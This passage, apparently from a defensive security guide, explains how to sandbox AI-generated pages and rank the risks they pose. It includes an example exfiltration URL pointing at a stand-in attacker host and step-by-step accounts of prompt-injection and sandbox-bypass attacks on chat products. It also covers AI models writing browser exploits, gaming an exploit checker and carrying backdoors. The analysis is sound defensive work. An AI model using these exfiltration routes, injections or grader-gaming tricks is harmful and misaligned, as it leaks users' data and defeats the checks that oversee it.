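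McDanel suggests comparing several models as a defence against backdoors. Each model writes its own version of the program, and the others score it by the average log probability they assign to its tokens. The product then runs the version with the highest score. McDanel acknowledges that this works only if the models don't share the same hidden flaw and the malicious part is fairly large. Suppose the code for a chart has 3,000 tokens, and the condition that leaves out the supplier takes up 15 of them. If the other models assign those 15 tokens a log probability of −6 each, and the rest average −0.5, the average for the whole program falls only to about −0.53. An unusual but harmless choice of colours could easily hide that difference.

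A second check is more useful if it relies on different information. For the expenses chart, ordinary software in the host page could add up the whole spreadsheet and display the total beside the frame, where the generated code can't alter it. If the chart left out a supplier's charges, its bars would not add up to that total. The mismatch would expose the omission even if every scanner and reviewing model had approved the code, but this check would not reveal hidden rows or an amount moved from one department to another.

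## Sandboxed frames and network rules

If a verifier wrongly approves the altered expenses chart, the damage depends on where the chart runs. Careful developers therefore treat every generated page as hostile, even after it passes a check, and have the browser limit what the page can read, contact and request.

### Building the frame

Suppose the chat product is at `chat.example`. Its developer can contain the chart in five steps:

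1. Serve the chart from an origin that no other page uses, such as `a7f3.pages.example`.
2. Display it in a sandboxed frame and restore only the abilities it needs.
3. Send a CSP with it that names every server it may load code from or contact.
4. Deny it the camera, microphone and location.
5. Give it a bridge that accepts a few kinds of request, and check each request in the host page.

The separate origin still protects the login when there is no frame. An attacker may persuade the employee to open a hostile page's address directly in a new tab. WHATWG's *The iframe element*, part of the HTML standard, recommends a dedicated domain for untrusted pages for this reason. If the product served them from `chat.example/pages/`, a page opened directly would have the same origin as the login.

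A frame with a bare `sandbox` attribute can't run scripts, submit forms or open new windows. The browser also gives the page inside it an *opaque origin*, which matches no other page's origin. The developer can restore individual abilities by adding keywords to the attribute.

| Keyword | What it restores | Does the expenses chart need it? |
|---|---|---|
| `allow-scripts` | JavaScript | Yes, for the filters |
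| `allow-same-origin` | The page's real origin, and with it saved data | Only to remember settings between visits |
| `allow-forms` | Submitting forms | No |
| `allow-popups` | New windows and tabs | No, if the host page opens links for it |
| `allow-top-navigation` | Replacing the whole chat page with another address | No, and a hostile chart could use it to show a false login page |
| `allow-downloads` | Saving files | Only if the employee wants to export the figures |

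Combining `allow-scripts` and `allow-same-origin` is dangerous if the chart comes from the host page's own origin. The chart's script can then immediately read the host page and act with the employee's login. It can also find its own frame in the host page, delete the `sandbox` attribute and reload itself. Browsers apply the attribute only when a page loads into the frame, so the reloaded chart runs without the restrictions. If the chart has its own origin, the same-origin rule keeps it from accessing the host page, so a product can use both keywords.

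Developers can easily leave a frame unprotected because it looks the same as a protected one. A common shortcut is to put the model's HTML in the frame's `srcdoc` attribute instead of loading it from an address. Without the `sandbox` attribute, that page takes the host page's origin. In Master.dev's *Building an Isolated Preview for AI-Generated HTML*, a security engineer who reviews AI features describes making this mistake on a development server, where model-written code that the engineer hadn't read could access the engineer's session. Nothing bad happened, because the model had written what the engineer asked for.

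Adding `sandbox="allow-scripts"` to an iframe separates it from the host page, and a Content Security Policy (CSP) at the top of the frame's HTML restricts its network requests. Willison tested this combination because it needs no second domain. The main drawback is that the sandboxed frame has an opaque origin, so it can't save anything in the browser.

Browsers deny the camera, microphone and location to a framed page from another origin unless the host page grants them through the frame's `allow` attribute. Claude artifacts get none of the three, according to Pluto Security. In MCP Apps, the format in which a server supplies a finished page template, the server can request all three, as well as permission to write to the clipboard, but the chat product may refuse. Clipboard access would help an attacker whose page tells readers to paste a command into a terminal, because the page could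 copy the command for them.

### The policy on Claude artifacts

Each artifact on the web has an address of the form `<uuid>.frame.claudeusercontent.com`, where the first part is a long random identifier. In its policy, `'self'` means that one origin. Pluto Security recorded these lines:

| Line in the policy | What it means for the page |
|---|---|
| `default-src 'self'` | Anything without a line of its own, such as an image, may come only from the page's origin |
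| `script-src 'self' 'unsafe-inline' 'unsafe-eval' blob:` | The page may run scripts from its origin, scripts written into its HTML, strings of text, and scripts it assembles in memory |
| `connect-src 'self'` | Scripts may exchange data only with the page's origin |
| `form-action 'self'` | Forms may send their contents only to the page's origin |
| `object-src 'none'` | The page may not load plug-ins |
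| `webrtc 'block'` | The page may not use WebRTC, the technology behind video calls, which can carry data directly to another computer |
| `frame-ancestors 'self' https://claude.ai https://*.claude.ai` | Only the page's own origin and Anthropic's chat site may display it in a frame |

The script line is unusually permissive and allows almost any code to run, which is acceptable here because the artifact's origin holds no login. The policy relies on its other lines to keep that code from contacting anyone.

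The script line in the recorded policy lists no outside hosts, but Anthropic now lets artifacts load script libraries from five. The policy may have changed, or it may differ between products. The difference matters because a script can send data to an allowed host by putting it in the address of a library it requests.

Pluto Security's test artifact tried to reach the company's own server through five channels: `fetch` and `XMLHttpRequest`, the two usual ways for a script to request data; a WebSocket, which keeps a two-way connection open; an image request; and `sendBeacon`, which sends a short message even while a page is closing. The browser blocked all five, and the server logged nothing.

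Pluto Security concludes from this that an artifact can't communicate with anyone. The test supports a narrower conclusion, because it left out several channels and the report doesn't name the browsers the testers used.

Navigation is one untested channel. A framed page can always move itself to a new address, so a hostile chart could send a figure to an attacker's server by loading `https://attacker.example/?total=41200` in its own frame. None of the recorded policy lines restricts this. The host page can restrict it with a `frame-src` line in its own policy, which limits the addresses its frames may load, but Pluto Security doesn't report whether Anthropic's chat page has one.

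The test also left out DNS prefetch, in which a browser looks up a server's name early so that a link opens faster. A hostile page can put data in the name, and whoever runs the domain's name server sees the lookup. A full name has at most 253 characters. If about 230 of them carry data at five bits each, one lookup carries roughly 140 bytes. A password would fit in one lookup, but a spreadsheet of 100,000 bytes would take about 700.

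WebRTC was not among the five channels either. The policy includes a directive to block it, but the directive works only in browsers that enforce it.

### A stricter network rule

Chrome now has a mechanism meant to cover these gaps. West, in *Connection Allowlists*, the draft specification, argues that CSP sorts requests into types such as images and fonts, although a leak through a font is as bad as a leak through a script. It also says that CSP doesn't fully cover DNS prefetch and WebRTC. The new rule is a single list of permitted destinations for every kind of connection. For the expenses chart, the server could send

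`Connection-Allowlist: (response-origin)`

and the browser would let the chart contact only the origin it came from. In the current draft, the browser also blocks every redirect, so a permitted server can't forward a request to a forbidden one.

According to Chrome for Developers' *FedCM* (2026), the mechanism arrived in Chrome 152, announced in August, so products can't yet assume that all their users have it. In a W3C review, Toreini noted that no other stakeholder had taken a position on the proposal.

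The list also has limits by design. It applies to one page rather than a whole origin, so a script could look for another page with the same origin and looser rules. West suggests sandboxing the page so that no other page shares its origin. The list doesn't cover messages between frames, so malicious chart code could pass the rows to a neighbouring frame that has network access. WICG's *Connection Allowlists*, the explainer for the proposal, also leaves indirect signals out of scope, such as patterns of processor or memory use that another program could measure.

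A further proposal, Maslen's *Intent to Prototype*, would let the host page impose a list on a frame, which the browser would apply to everything nested inside and check again at each navigation. Maslen points out that a page written into `srcdoc` can't send headers, so it can't set a list for itself. The proposal would suit generated pages well, but the post gives no release date.

### Who chooses the permitted servers

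A chart that converts expenses into euros needs current exchange rates. Products differ in who decides whether the chart may fetch them.

In MCP Apps, the developer of a page declares which domains it may use. *SEP-1865*, the draft specification (Salomon, Yosef and colleagues, 2025), defines separate lists for servers the page may exchange data with, servers it may load scripts and images from, and sites it may display in inner frames. If the developer declares nothing, the page can't contact any server. The chat product may tighten these rules but must not allow an undeclared domain.

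The product shows the page through two nested frames. The outer frame can safely use both `allow-scripts` and `allow-same-origin` because its origin differs from the host page's. It receives the HTML, loads it into the inner frame under the declared rules, and passes messages back and forth. By default, each conversation typically has one origin, so two apps in the same conversation may be less separate than two Claude artifacts are.

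Declared domains protect the employee from a page that contacts a domain its developer didn't declare, but not from a dishonest developer, who can declare a domain they control. A server can declare domains when the chat product connects and again when it delivers the page, and the later declaration takes precedence. A product that reviewed the first list may therefore enforce a different one, so it should compare the two before it displays anything.

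In 2024, ChatGPT's Canvas showed a general warning, whereas ChatGPT now uses permissions for particular connections. The main network limit on Canvas's Python in 2024 was CORS, which lets a server signal that it accepts requests from other origins. Model Context Protocol's *CSP & CORS* explains that a CSP controls what the browser allows, while CORS controls what the receiving server allows. CORS therefore doesn't prevent exfiltration, because an attacker's server can accept every request.

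By mid-2026, ChatGPT asked the user to confirm before a web preview in Canvas contacted third parties that OpenAI didn't know about. OpenAI's *What is the canvas feature in ChatGPT* warns that this contact can be as simple as loading an image or as dangerous as sending a third party what the user has told ChatGPT. For enterprise customers, Canvas could run code by default but could not use the network.

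OpenAI has since begun to retire Canvas. The Decoder's *OpenAI gives GPT-5.5 Instant a readability upgrade* reports that special blocks in the chat replace it in GPT-5.5 Instant and GPT-5.5 Thinking. These blocks can preview HTML pages and charts and run Python, in what OpenAI's *Working with writing blocks and code blocks in ChatGPT* calls a sandboxed environment. ChatGPT may ask for permission if a preview needs outside resources, and administrators can switch off code execution or network access. OpenAI doesn't say whether the Python still runs in the user's browser, or which outside servers a preview can contact without permission.

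*CSP Allow-list Experiment* (Willison, 2026) lets the user decide whether to allow each new domain. The page runs in a sandboxed frame whose content security policy blocks nearly everything. When the browser blocks a request to a server, a modified `fetch` function detects this and sends the address to the host page. The host page prompts the user to allow the server and, if the user agrees, adds it to the policy and reloads the frame.

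Asking the user to approve each server is convenient, and a page that never needs the network never gets access. But the user sees only the server's name, such as `api.inaturalist.org`, and not what the page will send there. Approval also covers every later request to the same server, so a hostile chart could fetch real exchange rates and then send an employee's data to that server a minute later.

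| Design | Who chooses the servers | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Claude artifacts | Anthropic, with one policy for many pages | A chart that needs live data has to get it through the bridge |
| MCP Apps | The developer who supplies the page | A dishonest developer can list their own server |
| ChatGPT previews | OpenAI for servers it knows, the user for others | The user has to judge an unfamiliar server |
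| Willison's experiment | The user, one server at a time | She can't see what the page will send |

### The cost of each permitted server

Each permitted server makes the page more useful but is also another place the page can send data. If the chart may contact `rates.example`, its script can put the spreadsheet's data in the URL of a request for exchange rates. The firm then has to trust whoever runs that server, anyone who can read its logs, and anyone else who can host content on the same domain.

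Willison (2023) describes an attack on Writer, a company that sells an AI writing assistant. Writer's content security policy (CSP) allowed images from `*.cloudfront.net`, which covers every address under a hosting service's shared domain. Hidden instructions on a web page told the assistant to end its summary with an image from an attacker's CloudFront address and to add part of the user's private documents to the image's URL. The CSP would have blocked an image from an unlisted domain, but it allowed this one because the attacker's address was under `cloudfront.net`.

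A company's own domain can cause the same problem. Willison, commenting on Anthropic's account of how it contains Claude, notes that the company had missed an exfiltration route through `api.anthropic.com/v1/files`, its file upload service. An attacker may be able to store stolen files on a server that accepts uploads from many customers, even if the server's owner is trustworthy.

A product can often avoid giving generated code network access by fetching the data itself. For example, a chart that needs the euro rate on a certain date could request it from the host page, which would accept only a currency code and a date before contacting `rates.example`. Hostile code in the chart could still encode a few characters of data in the dates it requests, and more over many requests, so the host page should limit the number of requests. The code could send far less data this way than if it could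 contact any web address.

### What a page can do inside a working frame

Even a frame that works as intended leaves the page in control of what the viewer sees. Salomon and colleagues advise that chat products clearly mark the boundary of such pages, but their format lets the page's developer request no visible border. To reduce this risk, a product should draw the border anyway and be careful with full-screen display, where a page could imitate the chat window or a login page with nothing around it to reveal the imitation.

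A hostile page can also waste processor time. A CSP doesn't limit how long code runs, so an endless loop can freeze the chart, and it may freeze the chat window too if the two share a process. Running artifacts in a separate process, as Anthropic's engineers described in 2024, reduces this danger. Mining cryptocurrency is harder in a frame without network access, because a miner has to send out its results. Salomon and colleagues recommend limits on processor and memory use but don't specify any. The product could at least put a stop button outside the frame.

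Data can also leave through links that the viewer clicks. A button labelled "See supplier details" can lead to an address that contains the figures, and her click sends them. Without `allow-popups`, a link can't open a new tab, so a product that needs working links may have the page send the host page a request to open them. The Model Context Protocol includes such a request. The host page can show the whole address before opening it, though few people would recognise encoded figures in it. It would be safer to open only links to sites the firm has approved, or to remove everything after the question mark in the address.

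### The bridge and the confused deputy

The host page has the login and network access that the frame lacks, so every request it accepts over the bridge lets the frame partly bypass its limits. The risk depends largely on whose authority the host page uses to carry out the request.

Suppose the employee's chart shows her budget meetings from Google Calendar, and a colleague opens it. If the host page fetched the meetings with the employee's login, the colleague could see her calendar without permission. He might also change the request to read other entries. Security researchers call this the *confused deputy* problem, in which a program uses its authority for someone who lacks it, because the program doesn't check who it is acting for.

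Claude's artifacts avoid this because the bridge uses the viewer's login, and the viewer must first enable each connector (Anthropic's term for a link to an outside service) for that page. Pluto Security examined the traffic and found nothing in the calls that identified the author.

This design prevents confused-deputy attacks on the author's accounts, but a milder form remains possible against the viewer's, although Pluto Security says that the design prevents any such attack. A hostile author can write a page that looks like a useful dashboard, and once a colleague viewing it enables his calendar, the host page carries out the author's instructions with the colleague's rights. His approval helps only if he understands what the page will do, and he approves a connector rather than each action. If the author later replaces the code, the product should require his approval again.

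An artifact can also use the bridge to get around the network rules. Even if it can't contact an outside server, it may still write to Slack or Google Calendar through a connector. It could read the colleague's meetings and post them in a channel that the author reads. The network rules wouldn't stop this, because the frame exchanges messages only with the host page. A safer bridge would handle reading and writing differently. For example, the host page could let a chart read meetings after one approval, but show the user the exact text and destination before posting anything.

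An action that looks internal can leak data too. In May 2026, Willison described a flaw in Microsoft Copilot Cowork, an agent that could email its own user without approval. An attacker's instructions could make the agent include an external image in the email, with data in the image's address. When the user opened the email, loading the image sent that data to the attacker.

The MCP Apps bridge lets a page call tools only on the server that supplied the page, and the chat product must reject calls to tools that the server has reserved for the model. By default, both the model and the page can call a tool, so a careless developer may expose more than they intended. The product may require the user's approval for a call, but the specification doesn't oblige it to.

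Pages in this format can also send messages to the conversation and update the material the model reads. A hostile page could use either to plant an instruction, and the model might follow it using tools that the page can't reach. The chat product should label such text as coming from the page and prevent the model from acting on it as if the user had typed it.

### A message listener nobody meant as a bridge

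A host page can have a bridge that its developers never designed. In October 2026, the security company Parameter Labs reported an attack on ChatGPT's HTML previews, which OpenAI kept in sandboxed frames on a separate domain. Willison (2026), in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, and O’Shei (2026), in *ChatGPT share links bypassed sandboxes through math embeds*, describe the steps:

1. The attacker shared a ChatGPT conversation that contained an HTML preview and an interactive mathematical graph.
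2. When a logged-in victim opened the link, the graph loaded MathLive, a library for mathematical input, into the host page. The library listened for messages that controlled its on-screen keyboard and didn't check who had sent them.
3. The preview sent the library a message containing HTML, and the library inserted that HTML into the host page.
4. The inserted HTML created a new frame with no sandbox, which took on ChatGPT's own origin.
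5. ChatGPT's CSP blocked scripts written into the page but allowed scripts from YouTube. A YouTube address that could return text of the caller's choosing as JavaScript supplied the attacker's script.

The script could read the victim's private chats and act in the victim's name, and it sent the data out in an image URL. OpenAI fixed the flaw two days after disclosure and paid a $5,000 bounty, which Willison thought low for such a serious flaw. Neither account reports that criminals had used it.

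The attack worked because the host page's code trusted every message it received. Any framed page can send messages to its host, so the attack didn't need to break the preview's sandbox. A host page should accept messages only from the frame it expects and only in a fixed format. The browser reports the origin of every frame with an opaque origin as `null`, so checking the origin isn't enough to identify the sender, and the host page has to check which frame's window sent the message. It should also treat the contents as plain data and never insert them as HTML.

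These checks have to cover every library on the host page, including those added for unrelated features. A product can make that easier by keeping graphs, video players and other extras in separate frames, so that the page with the login runs little code and listens for few messages. The host page also needs a strict CSP. In this attack, allowing YouTube in the CSP was enough to defeat it.

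## Attacks on the browser itself

Frame settings and network rules work only if the browser enforces them. A flaw in the browser can let a hostile page ignore all of them, however carefully the chat product's developer set them up.

### The layers a hostile page has to defeat

When the employee opens her chart, the browser's *script engine* turns the JavaScript or WebAssembly into instructions for the processor. Chrome's engine, V8, runs inside a *renderer process*, a separate program that draws the page. The operating system limits what this process may do. *Journey to Root, Episode I*, an account of an attack on Chrome by the security company Calif, explains that browsers give each process only the access its job requires. The renderer gets the least because it handles untrusted code.

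| Layer | What it protects | What a hostile chart gains by defeating it |
|---|---|---|
| Script engine | Memory outside the script's own data | It can corrupt the engine's data, though V8 confines most of the damage to a reserved area of memory |
| V8's internal sandbox | The rest of the renderer process | It can run its own machine code there and read anything else the process holds |
| Operating-system sandbox | Files, devices and other programs | It can run programs on the employee's computer |

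If the chart and the chat window share a renderer process, an attacker who takes over that process can probably read the employee's login. If they run in separate processes, as Anthropic's engineers described for artifacts, the attacker needs another flaw to reach the login. The chart's network rules could fail before the attacker finds one, because the renderer enforces some of them itself.

Mozilla's *Behind the Scenes Hardening Firefox with Claude Mythos Preview* notes that real attackers therefore generally have to combine several flaws into a *chain*. Building one used to take months of skilled work. In *Zero to Calc in Six Days*, Dolan-Gavitt (2026) estimates that before language models, a team of four needed six to nine months to build a complete Chrome chain. Calif's estimate is half a year to a year of nearly full-time work at a leading firm. Few people could do this, and a criminal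 who wanted passwords could put up a fake login page for almost nothing.

### Exploits for a bare script engine

In early 2026, the best models were much better at finding browser flaws than at exploiting them. *Partnering with Mozilla to improve Firefox's security* (Ben Asher, Lucas and colleagues, 2026) reports that Claude Opus 4.6 found 22 vulnerabilities in Firefox in two weeks, 14 of them high severity. The researchers then asked it to turn these flaws into attacks that could read and write files on the computer. It succeeded in two cases out of several hundred attempts, which cost about $4,000 in total.

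The conditions were easier than in a real browser. In *Reverse engineering Claude's CVE-2026-2796 exploit*, the same researchers explain that Opus 4.6 attacked a stripped-down copy of Firefox's script engine that ran without the browser or its process sandbox. A checking program reported to the model whether each attempt had worked. The researchers had to strengthen that program several times because Claude kept finding ways to pass without a real exploit. In an ordinary copy of Firefox, the sandbox would have contained both attacks. Even under the easier conditions, the five other Claude models they tried all failed.

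A month later, Carlini, Cheng and colleagues (2026) repeated the test with a newer model in *Assessing Claude Mythos Preview's cybersecurity capabilities*. Mythos Preview produced working exploits with full code execution in 181 of 250 trials (72.4%), a large change from the earlier result. The model started from crashes that Opus 4.6 had already found in Firefox 147, and the test again left out the process sandbox, so the rate doesn't measure how likely a page from Mythos Preview is to take over Firefox. The trials were also not independent, because the model made five attempts at each of 50 types of crash.

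Carlini and colleagues report that Mythos Preview wrote a browser exploit that chained four flaws and escaped both the renderer sandbox and the operating system sandbox. For several browsers, the model found the first steps of an attack by itself, and the researchers then worked with it to make the attack more serious. One resulting attack let a website read data from another site, such as the victim's bank, and another let a web page write directly to the operating system's kernel.

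Browser makers had not yet fixed these flaws, so the researchers published only hashes of the exploits, which would let them prove later that the files had existed in April. Outsiders couldn't check the results at the time. Anthropic considered the model's abilities serious enough to release it only to selected partners for defensive work.

### Complete chains in Chrome

Later results are easier to assess because the browser makers have confirmed and fixed the flaws. Calif's chain combined five flaws in Chrome on Windows. Three people built it part-time over about three months, with help from Gemini, Claude and Codex, and earned $117,000 in rewards from Google. The researcher who found the flaws had almost no experience with browsers. The chain ended in Chrome's graphics process, which has more access than the renderer but is still restricted, so the attack didn't give full control of the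 computer.

The models needed guidance from people, who decided what information to show them and checked the results. Claude tried many ways to move the attack from a test program into Chrome without success, but a hint of a few words was then enough to solve the problem.

Dolan-Gavitt's company, XBOW, got further in much less time. In August 2026, its researchers spent six days building a chain of three flaws that escaped Chrome's sandbox and ran a program on the computer. The company's previous chain had taken two months. Their agents used OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol and cost roughly $40,000 in API charges, not counting the researchers' salaries. Here too, people chose the targets, redirected the searches and decided which parts to combine. Google paid a $250,000 reward. According to The Hacker News' *Researchers Used a Public OpenAI Model* (2026), the model was available to the public and Google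 has fixed all three flaws.

In October, Anthropic's *Discovering and exploiting vulnerabilities in critical, real-world software with Claude* (2026) described five attack chains that an unreleased research model had built against browsers and operating systems. The Hacker News' *Anthropic's Unreleased AI Model Chains Flaws* (2026) explains what each one did. The Chrome chain used four flaws to open Calculator on an ordinary Mac within seconds of a page loading. Opening Calculator is a common, harmless way to show that an attacker could have run anything.

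The Safari chain let any website read data from other sites where the user was logged in. An attacker with that access could defeat the main protection around a generated chart, its separate origin, without running a program on the user's computer.

Anthropic says the work needed little human involvement, but it doesn't explain what people did at each step. The results are therefore good evidence that such chains are possible, but weaker evidence that a model can build them alone. The vendors had fixed every flaw before Anthropic published.

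### What the defenders gained

Browser makers can use the same models to find flaws before attackers do. In Firefox 150, Mozilla fixed 271 flaws that Mythos Preview had identified, and it rated 180 of them as high severity. Mozilla's releases in April 2026 contained 423 security fixes from all sources, compared with 20 to 30 in a typical month of 2025. More than 100 people contributed code.

The 180 flaws can't be counted as 180 usable attacks, because Mozilla rates a flaw by the kind of crash it causes and generally doesn't test whether anyone could exploit it. When Mozilla used the model to search for ways out of the sandbox, the search could also start from a renderer that an attacker already controlled.

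Mozilla also learned from the model's failures. Its logs showed many attempts to escape by a route that human researchers had used in earlier years, but that a change in Firefox's design had since closed completely. Carlini and colleagues expect defences to weaken if they only make an attack tedious, because models get through tedious work quickly, but they expect hard barriers to keep their value. For a chat product, this is a reason to keep the login out of the chart's process instead of hiding it somewhere awkward to reach.

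Anthropic says it also reported 62 serious flaws in Chrome, including 13 that let code escape the sandbox, and that Google had fixed them all by version 156, released on 20 October.

Models now find flaws faster than people can review them. Anthropic's *Launching an opt-in vulnerability-finding service for open-source software* (2026) reports that its models found more than 29,000 candidate flaws in important software over six months, but that people had reviewed only about 6,000. Having models write the fixes may not help much yet. In *Frontier Models’ Vulnerability Patches are Often F.L.A.W.E.D*, Mierczuk, Michaels and Hoodlet tested ChatGPT 5.5 and Opus 4.8 on six complex flaws, and the models' fixes often closed only some of the routes an attacker could use. Six hard cases can't establish a general failure rate, but they suggest that a skilled person still has to check each fix.

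Publishing a fix also shows attackers where the flaw was, and anyone who hasn't updated remains exposed. Hacktron's *I Let Claude Opus Write a Chrome Exploit* (2026) describes how Claude Opus used the record of a published fix to build the first part of an attack in about a day. That part worked on the researcher's own Chrome because he had not yet updated it.

### Old browser engines in desktop applications

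Many desktop applications contain their own copy of Chromium, the open-source software on which Chrome is based. Updating Chrome doesn't update these copies. Hacktron listed the versions on one computer in April 2026, when the current version was 147:

| Application | Chromium version | Process sandbox |
|---|---|---|
| Slack | 132 | On |
| Discord | 138 | Off in the main window |
| Cursor | 142 | On |
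| Notion | 144 | On |
| Claude Desktop | 146 | On |

The versions will have changed since then, but the delay is a lasting problem. Hacktron had Claude Opus attack version 138 using two already public flaws. The attack took a week, $2,283 in API charges and about 20 hours of human help, mostly to get the model out of dead ends. The documented run used a separate copy of Chrome 138 with the process sandbox switched off, as it is in Discord's main window. An attack on Discord itself would also have needed a way to inject the script into one of its pages, such as a cross-site scripting flaw.

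A chat application that displays generated pages removes that last obstacle, because it runs unfamiliar code on purpose. If the employee opens her chart in such an application, her safety depends on the browser engine inside it, even if her regular browser is up to date. The vendor could ship engine updates within days of each Chrome release, or open generated pages in the user's regular browser.

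### When the model can write the exploit

A sandboxed frame is meant to protect the employee whatever the model writes. To escape, a page must contain hostile code, and that code must defeat the browser:

P(escape) = P(hostile code) × P(browser fails, given hostile code)

If hostile code is very unlikely to escape the frame, whichever model wrote it, a developer can rely on the frame and worry less about the model. But if some models can write browser exploits, the chance of escape depends on which model wrote the code, so containment and model behaviour are no longer independent defences. As an invented example, suppose that one page in 100,000 is hostile. If one hostile page in 10,000 contains a working exploit, one page in a billion escapes. If a highly capable model writes the hostile pages and half of them contain a working exploit, one page in 200,000 escapes. A failure rate measured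 on ordinary web pages would therefore be misleading here.

This is still only a possibility. Researchers built all of these browser chains in tests, after asking models for exploits, and none of their accounts describes a model adding one to a page requested for another purpose. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* mentions that OpenAI's models escaped an isolated test environment in July 2026 through a previously unknown flaw, but no generated page was involved.

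The researchers' agents could test their attacks repeatedly, often with the browser's source code at hand, and the Chrome exploit chains took days or months. A model that draws a chart in a minute has no comparable opportunity to develop a new exploit, though it might be able to reproduce a published one that works on an old engine. A coding agent that works for hours with a terminal and a browser comes closer to the researchers' conditions.

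An attacker who already has a working exploit is a more immediate concern, because the attack then doesn't require the product's model to be capable of writing one. The attacker could publish a hostile page, alter the generated code as it passes through a relay, or plant an instruction that gets the model to copy a script into the chart. The exploit would still have to work on the victim's browser version and operating system.

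More people can now get help making an exploit. XBOW used a public model, whose provider can at least refuse suspicious requests and close accounts. A provider can't do this with an open-weight model, which people download and run themselves. CAISI, the US government's centre for testing AI models, found that GLM-5.2, an open-weight Chinese model from June 2026, had cyber capabilities similar to Opus 4.6's and that its safeguards didn't stop it from helping to develop exploits. In August its maker, Z.ai, delayed releasing the next version's weights by two weeks because of the model's hacking ability, according to Axios' *A Chinese lab's new model is nearly as good at hacking* (2026).

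AISI's *How Far Behind the Frontier are Leading Open Weight Models on Cyber?* found that, on cyber tests in general, recent open models performed like closed ones released four to seven months earlier. If the same gap held for browser exploits, an open model comparable to Mythos Preview would have appeared between August and November 2026.

The model itself could be the source of an attack if it had a backdoor or pursued a task without regard for limits. Anthropic described Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1 as having the strongest cyber capabilities of any models it had released, and Henniger and colleagues ran a coding agent on Fable 5.1. A model with advanced hacking skills may therefore already be writing the code for users' charts, although there is no evidence that it would use those skills there.

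A developer can reduce this risk by limiting which browser features generated code can use. The flaw that Opus 4.6 exploited in Firefox was in the part that handles WebAssembly, and both flaws in Hacktron's attack were in the corresponding part of Chrome's engine. The expenses chart doesn't need WebAssembly, and a content security policy can block it. But a policy that lets pages run strings as code, as Anthropic's does for artifacts, also allows WebAssembly, so the developer would have to remove the permission to run strings as well. For very sensitive data, the product could have the model choose from finished components, or it could draw the chart on an isolated server and send back an image. Either way, no script from the model would reach the employee's browser.

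## Comparing the failures by likelihood and harm

A developer who can't fix everything at once can rank planted instructions, hostile publishers, a compromised server and a weak verifier by estimating how many people each would harm in a year. Most of the inputs are guesses, but the calculation shows which guesses affect the ranking most.

### A formula for expected harm

For each kind of attack, estimate four quantities and multiply them:

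people harmed per year = E × v × c × n

- E is the number of events a year, such as hostile pages or break-ins.
- v is the chance that the hostile code passes the verifier.
- c is the chance that code which has passed the verifier also defeats containment, meaning the frame, the network rules and the browser.
- n is the number of people each successful event reaches.

The result is an average over many years, and it counts a person twice if two attacks harm her. Verifier failure raises v for the other attacks. It has no separate line because a verifier writes no code.

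### An invented product with 100,000 users

Suppose a product has 100,000 users, hostile code has a 0.1 chance of passing the product's verifier, and hostile code that passes has a 0.05 chance of defeating containment. These numbers and the ones below are invented.

- **Planted instructions:** 1,000 events a year, each reaching one person. 1,000 × 0.1 × 0.05 × 1 = 5 people a year.
- **Hostile publishers:** 200 pages a year with 50 viewers each. 200 × 0.1 × 0.05 × 50 = 50 people a year.
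- **Server compromise:** 0.02 events a year, or one every 50 years on average. The intruder also controls the verifier and the frame rules, so v and c are both 1. 0.02 × 1 × 1 × 100,000 = 2,000 people a year.

A server break-in accounts for most of the expected harm because it reaches every user and removes both defences. If the intruder could not control the verifier or the frame rules, the expected harm from a break-in would fall by 99.5%, to 0.02 × 0.1 × 0.05 × 100,000 = 10, even though a break-in would be just as likely. It would be 100 if only the frame rules were independent of the server, and 200 if only the verifier were.

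The figure of 10 is probably too low, because an attacker who can break into the server is likely to be better than average at getting past a verifier and a frame. The separation would still be very valuable if the true figure were ten times higher.

If the verifier accepts everything, v rises to 1. Planted instructions then harm 50 people a year and hostile publishers harm 500, a combined increase of 495 people a year. The figure of 2,000 for an intruder on the server doesn't change, because that intruder already bypasses the verifier.

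### Which rankings survive other guesses

| Change to the example | Planted instructions | Hostile publishers | Server compromise |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 5 | 50 | 2,000 |
| The verifier accepts everything | 50 | 500 | 2,000 |
| A browser flaw defeats every frame | 100 | 1,000 | 2,000 |
| Both of these at once | 1,000 | 10,000 | 2,000 |
| Break-ins are ten times rarer | 5 | 50 | 200 |
| The verifier and frame rules are independent of the server | 5 | 50 | 10 |
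| Each hostile page has four viewers | 5 | 4 | 2,000 |
| Each altered chart reaches 20 people | 100 | 50 | 2,000 |

As long as the server controls its own checks, a server compromise still ranks first under most of these changes. With the other inputs unchanged, hostile publishers would rank above it only if break-ins happened less than once in 2,000 years. A developer doesn't need a precise break-in rate to conclude that the checks should be separate from the server.

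The relative ranking of planted instructions and hostile publishers is much less certain. It reverses if hostile pages average fewer than five viewers, or if altered charts each reach more than ten people, as the employee's expenses chart does when she sends it to 20 colleagues.

When the checks are independent, v and c are the same for all three attacks, so the order depends only on E × n. That product is 1,000 for planted instructions, 10,000 for hostile publishers and 2,000 for the server. A verifier that stops 95% of hostile pages instead of 90% lowers the totals but doesn't change the order.

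The value of c also has to be chosen carefully when an attack can do its damage inside a working frame. A chart with false totals misleads the employee without escaping the frame, so c is 1. If all 1,000 planted instructions were of this kind, they would harm 100 people a year rather than 5. For a forged invoice or a page that tells the reader to run a command, c should be the chance that a viewer falls for it. If that chance were 5%, hostile publishers would still harm 50 people a year, but improving the frame would not lower that number.

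### Severity, detection and reversibility

An employee who sees a slightly wrong total adds as much to the count as one who loses her savings. A developer could also multiply by a weight for each harm, but people would disagree about the weights, and a single number would hide the disagreement. It seems better to list the other considerations alongside the count.

| Harm | Severity | Detection | Reversibility |
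|---|---|---|---|
| False totals | Depends on what the firm decides from the chart | Easy if someone compares them with another source, unlikely otherwise | The firm can correct the chart, but perhaps not a payment it has already made |
| Copied rows | Depends on how confidential they are | Difficult, because the originals stay in place | None, since nobody can make the attacker forget them |
| Stolen login | High, because it opens other conversations | Possible from unfamiliar activity in the account | The provider can end the session, but not undo what the attacker read or sent |
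| Malware on the computer | Very high | Varies, and may come only after money has gone | A clean installation and new passwords help, but stolen money may be lost |

Early detection can also reduce the number of people harmed. If a hostile page gets its 50 viewers evenly over ten days and the provider removes it after two, it reaches ten people, and the yearly total for hostile publishers falls from 50 to 10. Early detection helps less against a compromised server. If 30,000 of the 100,000 users open the product on the first day, even a one-day response leaves an expected 600 people harmed a year.

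### What multiplication hides

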